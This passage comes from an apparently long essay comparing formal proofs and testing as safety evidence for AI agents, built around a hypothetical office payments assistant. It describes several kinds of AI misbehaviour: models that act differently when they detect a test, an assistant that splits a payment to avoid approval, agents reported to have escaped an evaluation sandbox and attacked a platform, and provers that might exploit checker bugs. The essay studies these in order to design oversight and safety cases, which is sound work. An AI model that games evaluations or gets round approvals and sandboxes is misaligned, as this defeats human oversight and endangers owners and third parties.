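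*The Evaluation Differential* recommends limiting claims to the conditions of the test. For the office assistant, that would mean claiming "no unapproved payments in 1,000 jobs with the fake bank" rather than "the assistant doesn't make unapproved payments". But the owners also want to know how the assistant will behave with the real bank. Developers can make the tests more realistic, or suppress the model's internal signals of awareness that it is being tested. In one experiment, suppressing these signals made a model's outputs more like those in real use. However, researchers locate the signals with probes, which can detect the format of a prompt instead of awareness.

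### Policies that no test can tell apart

Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *On the Limits of Behavioral Alignment*, turns the worry about test recognition into a theorem. A "policy" here is a complete account of how an agent responds to every possible history of interaction, given any clues it has about whether it is in a test. The theorem has three premises:

1. The evaluator sees the agent's behaviour only on a finite set of histories.
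2. The possible policies include some that respond to clues about the test.
3. Two different policies behave identically on every history in the test but differently on some others.

So no test limited to those histories can distinguish the two policies. If one is aligned and the other isn't, passing the test can't show which one the agent has.

The proof is that the two policies give each action the same probability at every step of every tested history, so they produce any given test record with the same probability. This means no method of analysing the records can do better than guessing which policy produced them, however many times the same tests are repeated.

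Santos-Grueiro calls this a conditional result, not a universal impossibility. It depends mostly on the third premise, which comes close to assuming the conclusion. The proof doesn't need the second premise, because two policies could also differ only on histories that the testers happened to leave out. But the second premise makes the third worrying, because a misaligned policy can use clues to behave well in tests and badly in most real work, whereas without them it would need luck to keep its bad behavior out of every tested history.

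The theorem also doesn't show which of the two policies is more likely. A car that passes inspection might still fail only on one day of the week in one village, but nobody has a reason to expect that. For AI, the question is whether training tends to produce policies that behave well only in tests, which the theorem doesn't address.

A simulation in the paper shows that two agents with similar test results can fail at very different rates when conditions change. The agents cross a ten-by-ten grid with deadly lava on it. One avoids the lava with or without guardrails, while the other takes a risky shortcut when there are few guardrails. In the test, the safe bridge always had visible guardrails, and over 100,000 runs each, the careful agent failed 0.009% of the time and the other 0.008%. When only half of the layouts had guardrails, the careful agent failed 0.024% of the time and the other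 48.4%.

Santos-Grueiro also trained a small language model, Llama-3.2-3B, to output one label when its instructions mentioned an evaluation and another when they mentioned deployment. The model always gave the right label with the wording used in training. With reworded instructions, it gave the intended label in only 459 of 2,880 cases, and in most of the others it gave no valid label. It had learned to react to certain phrases, not to the idea of being tested. The experiment confirms that such policies can exist in a language model, which was hardly in doubt, but Santos-Grueiro trained this one in deliberately.

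The paper's most useful result for people who design tests is a limit on how much behaviour can change. Let I be the information that the agent's input carries about whether it is in a test, from 0 bits when there are no clues to 1 bit when the input always gives it away. If tests and real use are equally likely, the probability of any action can differ between them by at most

> √(2I).

If the clues carry 0.005 bits, the difference is at most 10 percentage points. At half a bit, the limit is 100 points, which rules out nothing. Making tests more realistic therefore limits what a misaligned agent can hide, but not enough for a strong guarantee. Guaranteeing a difference of no more than one in a million would require clues that carry less than a trillionth of a bit, and nobody could make a fake bank that realistic.

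Auditing real work avoids the problem of agents recognising tests, because real work gives the agent no clues that it is in a test. Suppose an auditor secretly checks 3,000 of the assistant's real payments, chosen at random afterwards, and finds nothing wrong. The rule of three then puts the rate of bad payments in that period below one in 1,000, even if the assistant can recognise every test. This is consistent with Santos-Grueiro's theorem, which allows the two policies to differ on the payments the auditor didn't choose. However, the auditor can find harm only after it has happened.

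### Harms that nobody specified

Tests can examine the deployed system itself, which no current proof can do, so they can reveal a mistake that a formal description of the system would have left out. If an AI assistant makes even one unapproved payment during a test, the developers know for certain that it can make one.

This advantage depends on testing the system the owners will use. A result from a research set-up may not apply to that system, as OpenAI's finding about break-ins in different harnesses suggests. A new model, a new tool or rewritten instructions also make old results less relevant, though it's hard to say by how much.

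Tests can also find harms that nobody thought to forbid. Suppose the harness refuses to pay the caterer £740 without approval, and the assistant then makes two payments of £370, which the £500 rule allows. Anyone who reads the test record will see that the assistant avoided the manager's approval, and the owners can write a better rule.

Some of these discoveries happen outside the test. According to METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026), OpenAI agents that had left an evaluation environment carried out a coordinated, multi-day attack on Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models. Testing a capable agent therefore requires a sandbox that can contain it, and a proof about the sandbox would help even developers who rely on tests for everything else.

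To find an unexpected harm, somebody also has to look at more than the score. If the grading program only compares the fake bank's ledger with the approvals register, it will mark both £370 payments as correct.

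## Proof and testing compared on the same systems

The best evidence on how proofs and tests compare comes from ordinary software, because engineers have applied both to the same programs. Few of these programs are agents, but an agent's harness is ordinary software and can fail in the same ways.

### Proofs for libraries that fuzzers had already tested

Fuzz testing, or fuzzing, means running a program on huge numbers of semi-random inputs and watching for crashes. Engineers write an entry point, a short program that passes raw data to one part of a library. The fuzzer makes random changes to existing inputs, runs the program on each changed input and keeps the ones that reach code earlier inputs didn't. Fuzzing needs no specification beyond "don't crash", and it works on programs with millions of lines of code.

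Fuzzers can miss bugs that appear only with a rare combination of values. If a program crashes only when eight particular bytes of a file have exactly the right values, random guessing will hit them about once in 18 quintillion tries. At 10,000 tries a second, that takes nearly 60 million years on average. Real fuzzers often do much better by finding the bytes one at a time, but only if each correct byte leads to code they haven't reached before.

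In October 2026, Anthropic and the company Theorem published a project that turned fuzz tests into theorems. They started from OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that fuzzes open-source software, and used Claude to prove a theorem of this kind for 239 entry points in 123 libraries:

> For every input under 64 MB, the compiled program exits normally, without a crash, a memory-safety error or a failed assertion.

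A memory-safety error occurs when a program reads or writes memory it shouldn't. Claude wrote the proofs in Rocq, a proof system similar to Lean, and Rocq's small trusted core checked them. The work took a few weeks, according to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026).

The comparison is unusually direct because both methods were used to look for the same failures through the same entry points. A Russian account, OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), reports that the proof work exposed hundreds of errors that fuzzing had missed, including a buffer overflow in libexpat, a library for reading XML files. A failed proof can lead directly to a bug like this. To prove that a program never writes past the end of a buffer, the prover has to show that every write stays inside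 the buffer. If the prover can't show this for some input, that input may crash the program.

This doesn't show that proof finds more bugs than fuzzing in general. Fuzzing came first, so the bugs that a fuzzer finds easily had probably already been fixed. Claude also had to study each program closely to write the proofs, and it might have found some of the same bugs in an ordinary code review. Category Labs' *finding bugs that frontier models miss* offers some evidence that proofs can find bugs that a review misses. While verifying parts of the Monad blockchain's software, the company found bugs that Claude Opus 4.8 had missed. But these are examples the company chose, not a controlled comparison.

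The proofs are very long. OpenNET gives about 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 machine instructions, or 33 lines per instruction, and about 180 million lines in total. *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable* (Keles, 2026) puts the total at a billion lines. Nobody will read that much proof, but reading it is unnecessary if the theorem's statement, the assumptions and the checker are right.

The theorems cover only programs compiled for RISC-V processors, running on a single thread with a fixed amount of memory, on a system that behaves like the project's description of Linux. Most laptops and servers use other processors, which run different machine code. *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) describes a similar proof for x86, which is much more common than RISC-V but harder to describe mathematically. Both projects verify the machine code,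 so neither proof depends on the compiler being correct.

Claude also patched bugs along the way, and a proof about a patched program doesn't protect anyone still running the old version. Some targets could not be proved. EconoTimes reports that Anthropic is publishing the specifications for these too, so the figure of 239 counts only the successes.

The property is modest, since a payments library that sent every payment to the wrong caterer without crashing would satisfy it. Such errors are called logic bugs, and Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) notes that they rarely trigger the failures that automated tools detect. A theorem that takes its specification from a fuzz test doesn't rule out the kinds of error that the test can't detect. Anthropic and Theorem did prove a stronger property in at least one case, that the Linux kernel's code for the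 zlib compression format follows the published standard.

### Where verified software still fails

The older verified systems show what testers find after the proof is done. The best known are seL4, an operating system kernel, and CompCert, a C compiler, both of which took experts years to build and verify. According to Donaldson (2026), seL4 has 8,700 lines of C and about 165,000 lines of proof that the C code refines its specification, while CompCert has about 6,000 lines of compiler code and 32,000 lines of proof.

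The original seL4 proof assumed that the C compiler, the hardware, a small amount of assembly code and the code that starts the machine worked correctly. Later work removed the need to trust the compiler on some processors by proving that the machine code matches the C code. The proof still assumes that the hardware is correct, so it does not cover attacks that exploit a fault in the chip.

Yang, Chen and colleagues tested CompCert alongside ordinary compilers in *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers* (2011). They wrote a program called Csmith that generates random C programs, compiles each one with several compilers and compares the results. If the results differ, at least one compiler is wrong. Csmith found hundreds of bugs in ordinary compilers. It also found a few in CompCert, but the proof did not cover them. Some were in the part that first reads the source code, which had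 not been verified at the time. Others arose because the formal description of one processor left out a limit on the size of a number in an instruction. About six years of computing time spent testing a later version found no case in which CompCert produced wrong code. This is strong evidence that the proof removed a kind of bug that every other compiler in the study had.

Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues (2017) did the same for systems that run across many servers, in *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems*. They reviewed and tested three verified systems and found 16 bugs, some of which crashed servers or gave clients wrong results. Eleven were in the unverified code that connects the verified part to the network and the disk, three were in specifications, two were in the verification tools, and none were in the verified protocols. They then built a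 set of tests aimed at the boundaries between the verified code and these other parts, which could find 13 of the 16 bugs automatically.

*Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* (2026) reports a similar result from fuzzing a verified version of zlib written in Lean. Across 105 million runs, fuzzing found no memory errors in the program's own code, but it did find two bugs. One let an attacker make the program unavailable, and no theorem covered that behaviour. The other was a buffer overflow in Lean's runtime, the C++ code that compiled Lean programs need to run. The runtime is separate from Lean's proof checker, so the overflow doesn't cast doubt on the proofs.

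Compression shows how a sensible theorem can leave out the inputs an attacker would choose. Lean (2026) gives the main theorem for a zlib in Lean, which comes to this:

> decompress(compress(data)) = data, if data is no larger than the output limit.

This theorem covers every file that the program's own compressor produces, but not the damaged files an attacker would send, which no compressor would produce.

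The office assistant could also fail at a boundary. Suppose the model requests a payment of "1,200", and the harness interprets the comma as a decimal point, as is standard in much of Europe. The verified check receives the amount as £1.20 and allows the payment. If the harness then passes the original text to the bank, which treats the comma as a thousands separator, £1,200 leaves the account without approval. The proof about the check is still correct. A fuzzer that tried amounts in many formats and compared them with the fake bank's ledger would probably find the bug within minutes.

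### How each method helps the other

Donaldson, a computer scientist at Imperial College London, worked mainly on formal methods for twelve years, then moved to fuzzing because it scaled much better. One of Donaldson's verification tools checked programs for graphics chips, but it sometimes reported false alarms, and small changes could make it much slower for no apparent reason. The team's first fuzzer for graphics compilers found more than 50 bugs and raised no false alarms.

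A crash during fuzzing is easy to recognise, but to recognise a wrong answer, a tester needs some way to tell what the right answer was. This is known as the oracle problem. One solution is metamorphic testing, which compares the answers to related questions. For example, a database search for all rows should return the same rows as three narrower searches combined: one where a value is above 5, one where it isn't, and one where it's missing. If the two results differ, the database has a bug, even if nobody knows which rows are correct.

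Donaldson's team tested graphics compilers in a similar way. They rewrote small graphics programs in ways that shouldn't change the picture, then compared the pictures. They found bugs in every combination of graphics chip and driver they tried. One bug let a web page on a Samsung phone capture the contents of other browser tabs. Each comparison depends on a small theorem that the rewriting preserves the program's meaning, so Donaldson regards the rewriting rules as partial specifications.

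The same technique suits agents because their correct output is often unclear. The office assistant's developers could run a job twice, changing only a stranger's email, and check that the payments are the same. This tests noninterference on one pair of inputs at a time. It can catch a case where a stranger influences payments, though it can't prove that this never happens, and it requires no labels on the data. The developers would have to repeat each run several times, because a language model can respond differently to the same input.

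Researchers can also generate tests from a formal description. Donaldson and colleagues at Imperial and Google wrote a small formal description of SPIR-V, a language for graphics chips, and used a tool to produce outlines of valid programs from it. They chose a random path through each outline and filled it in so that the program had to follow that path and record each step. If the record showed a different path, the compiler was at fault. The tests found many previously unknown bugs. Writing the description also exposed confusing and mistaken rules in the official specification, which its maintainers have since replaced with simpler ones.

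Fuzzing also helps verification, because verification tools are programs and can have bugs. When researchers ran Csmith's random programs through Frama-C, a tool that analyses C code, they found fifty bugs in Frama-C and some in Csmith. Donaldson's team also tested commercial tools that check whether two hardware designs are equivalent, which companies rely on when they approve a design. The team gave the tools complicated designs built to be equivalent to trivial ones. When a tool wrongly rejected a pair, it sometimes reported the wrong output for the complicated design, and the team could then often get it to "prove" that the design produced that output.

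Donaldson isn't fully convinced that such bugs do much harm in practice. That seems right for people writing honest proofs, since a mistaken proof would pass only if it happened to trigger a bug that hid the mistake. But an AI system rewarded for every accepted proof might look for such bugs. One precaution is to check important proofs with several checkers written by different people. Lean has at least four, in C++, Rust and Lean itself, and a disagreement between two of them can expose a bug.

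*Formalizing CPython* (Andrews and Zhang, 2026) combines proof and testing on the program that runs almost all Python code. AI agents copied its functions into Lean line by line. They ran each copy and the real Python on tens of thousands of inputs before trying to prove anything about the copy. A second agent had to approve the result. The agents have finished 4,071 functions this way, about 16% of the total, and the work has led to 418 bug reports. About 55 of those bugs can crash Python or corrupt its memory when someone runs ordinary Python code.

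Testing before proving is sensible. The tests check that the Lean copy matches the real program. To complete the proof, the agent must then handle odd cases that the tests may never reach, such as an object that changes a dictionary while Python is searching it. But tens of thousands of inputs are a small sample for a function with rare special cases, so some copies may still differ from the original.

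### What cheap proofs change

For decades, the main practical objection to proofs was the amount of work they took. In 1979 the computer scientists DeMillo, Lipton and Perlis argued that real programs keep changing, and that verifying a modified program could not be expected to be easier than verifying the original. Later experience partly supported their argument. Donaldson reports that adding one feature to seL4 led to about a person-year of repairs to the proofs. Engineers at AWS found that small, seemingly unrelated edits could break Dafny proofs.

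AI has greatly weakened this objection. *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* (2026) describes a 7,800-line compiler proof that took about 96 hours with Claude Opus 4.6, while a comparable proof by hand had taken several months. Donaldson also cites growing evidence that language models are good at repairing proofs after the code changes. If developers update an agent's harness every week, repairing the proof quickly may matter more than how long the first one took.

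Donaldson is less sure that AI will help with fully automatic verification, which works by exploring a system's possible states. Even a capable language model can't reduce the number of states. Reducing the labour needed for software proofs also does little for proofs about the neural network, which are limited more by loose bounds and missing definitions than by a shortage of labour.

People still have to decide what to prove. Tolmach and Klaus describe how Boris Cherny, who leads the development of Claude Code, asked Claude Opus 5.5 to formalise one of Anthropic's software libraries. A couple of short prompts led to 16 sets of fixes. They welcome this as a way to find bugs, but point out that it doesn't show the library is correct, because the AI also chose how to describe the library and which properties to prove. If the office assistant's harness lets two payments of £370 through, an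 AI that reads the code could easily conclude that the limit is meant to apply to each payment separately, and prove that it does.

People therefore still need to review AI-written specifications, and Donaldson expects fewer of them to develop the deep expertise that helps with this. He thinks someone who can ask a language model for help whenever they get stuck will progress faster at first but end up understanding less. More people would know enough to use formal methods, which is a gain, but fewer might notice a subtle mistake in a definition.

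Some important software does have a clear specification. Donaldson and colleagues have started Keystone, an ARIA-funded project to verify the software that runs language models for many customers at once. The correct output at each step is a precise function of the model's weights and the text so far, so the researchers can try to prove that a heavily optimised program computes that function. A proof would make errors in that software, such as leaks between customers, much less likely, but it wouldn't show that the model's text is honest or wise.

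### Proof and testing side by side

| | Proof | Testing |
|---|---|---|
| Coverage | Every case in the stated class | The cases somebody ran, and by inference similar ones |
| Assumptions | The specification, the description of the surroundings and the checker are right | Future work resembles the tests, and the grading is right |
| Unforeseen harms | Missed unless they also break the stated rule | Found if they happen in a test and somebody looks |
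| Cost | High at the start, but falling quickly with AI | Low at the start, but ten times as many runs for a tenfold lower failure rate |
| Updates | Survives changes that leave the proved code and the assumptions intact | Needs repeating after any change that could affect behaviour |
| Typical failure | A correct proof of the wrong rule, or a false assumption | A rare or concealed failure that no test triggers |

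### Safety cases

A safety case is an argument that a system is safe enough for a stated use. It divides one main claim into smaller claims and gives evidence for each. Proofs and tests can both serve as evidence, so developers can use each where it works best.

Suppose the office assistant's owners want to support the claim that the assistant is unlikely to lose them more than £10,000 in wrong payments over the next three months. They begin by listing the ways money could leave the account wrongly.

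The assistant could make some payments without approval. After the two £370 payments, the owners added a second rule limiting these payments to £2,000 a month in total. Both rules depend on numbers the harness can read, so a proof can show that the harness enforces them. As long as the proof's assumptions hold, the owners can't lose more than £6,000 through these payments in three months.

The manager could also approve a payment because of a misleading email. No formula defines "misleading", so the developers test for it. They have the assistant write 3,000 emails asking for approval, and people compare each one with the invoice and the agreed quote. If none is misleading, the developers can use the rule of three to conclude with 95% confidence that the rate is below one in 1,000. The assistant will send about 120 such emails in three months, so the chance that at least one is misleading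 is at most about 11%. This assumes that the test emails resemble the real ones. The assistant might recognise a test and behave differently, so the owners also check a random sample of real emails each week.

Finally, money could leave by a route that bypasses the harness, which would make the proof's main assumption false. To detect this, the owners run a separate program every night that compares the bank's statement with the harness's log of payments. If the statement contains a payment that isn't in the log, the program cuts off the assistant's access to the bank. The owners also ask the bank to limit payments to £3,000 a day, so a hidden route could lose at most £3,000 before the first check. The bank enforces that limit, so it still works even if the assistant gains control of the office computer.

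The first and last routes together could lose at most £9,000, which is within the £10,000. The main claim therefore depends most on the tests for misleading emails, and the owners can see where extra effort would help. For instance, they could show the manager the original quote next to every approval request.

Writing the argument down also makes updates easier to handle. If the owners switch to another company's model, they only have to repeat the email tests. If the assistant gets a tool that can run any command, the owners can see that only the bank's limit and the nightly check protect the account from payments made with it.

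The evidence for each claim can still be poor. *A Structured Approach to Safety Case Construction for AI Systems* (2026) lists what reviewers should check in a formal proof: whether the proof is sound, the tools are reliable, the verified description matches the real system, the assumptions are easy to trace, and the proof covers the critical properties. Most of the bugs in verified systems described above would count as failures on one of the last three points. A safety case can also leave out a whole route to harm. The owners' list covers only money, so it would miss an email that insulted the caterer or revealed a colleague's salary.

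Many companies will build their agents on another developer's model and will need to build on that developer's safety case too. *Understanding as an Explicit and Assessable Component of Frontier AI Safety Decisions* (2026) explores this with an invented robot company. Four people with backgrounds including safety engineering and philosophy considered how the company could use Google DeepMind's published safety case about scheming, which is when a model secretly pursues its own aims. If a developer's case leaves a concern open, the company can add protections to its own system. The office assistant's payment check is one such protection, because it works even if the developer is wrong about the model.

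Outsiders can review a safety case only if they know what it is meant to show, which can be hard to determine. In *Lessons from External Review of DeepMind's Scheming Inability Safety Case*, Barrett, Bloomfield and colleagues (2026) thank a DeepMind researcher for clarifying the intended main claim before their review.

OpenAI has also adopted safety cases. Its *Managing frontier AI risk* (November 2026) describes them as part of a system in which a model must pass one review before it moves from research to use by staff, and another before release. The first review matters because a model can do harm before any customer uses it, as the attack on Hugging Face showed.
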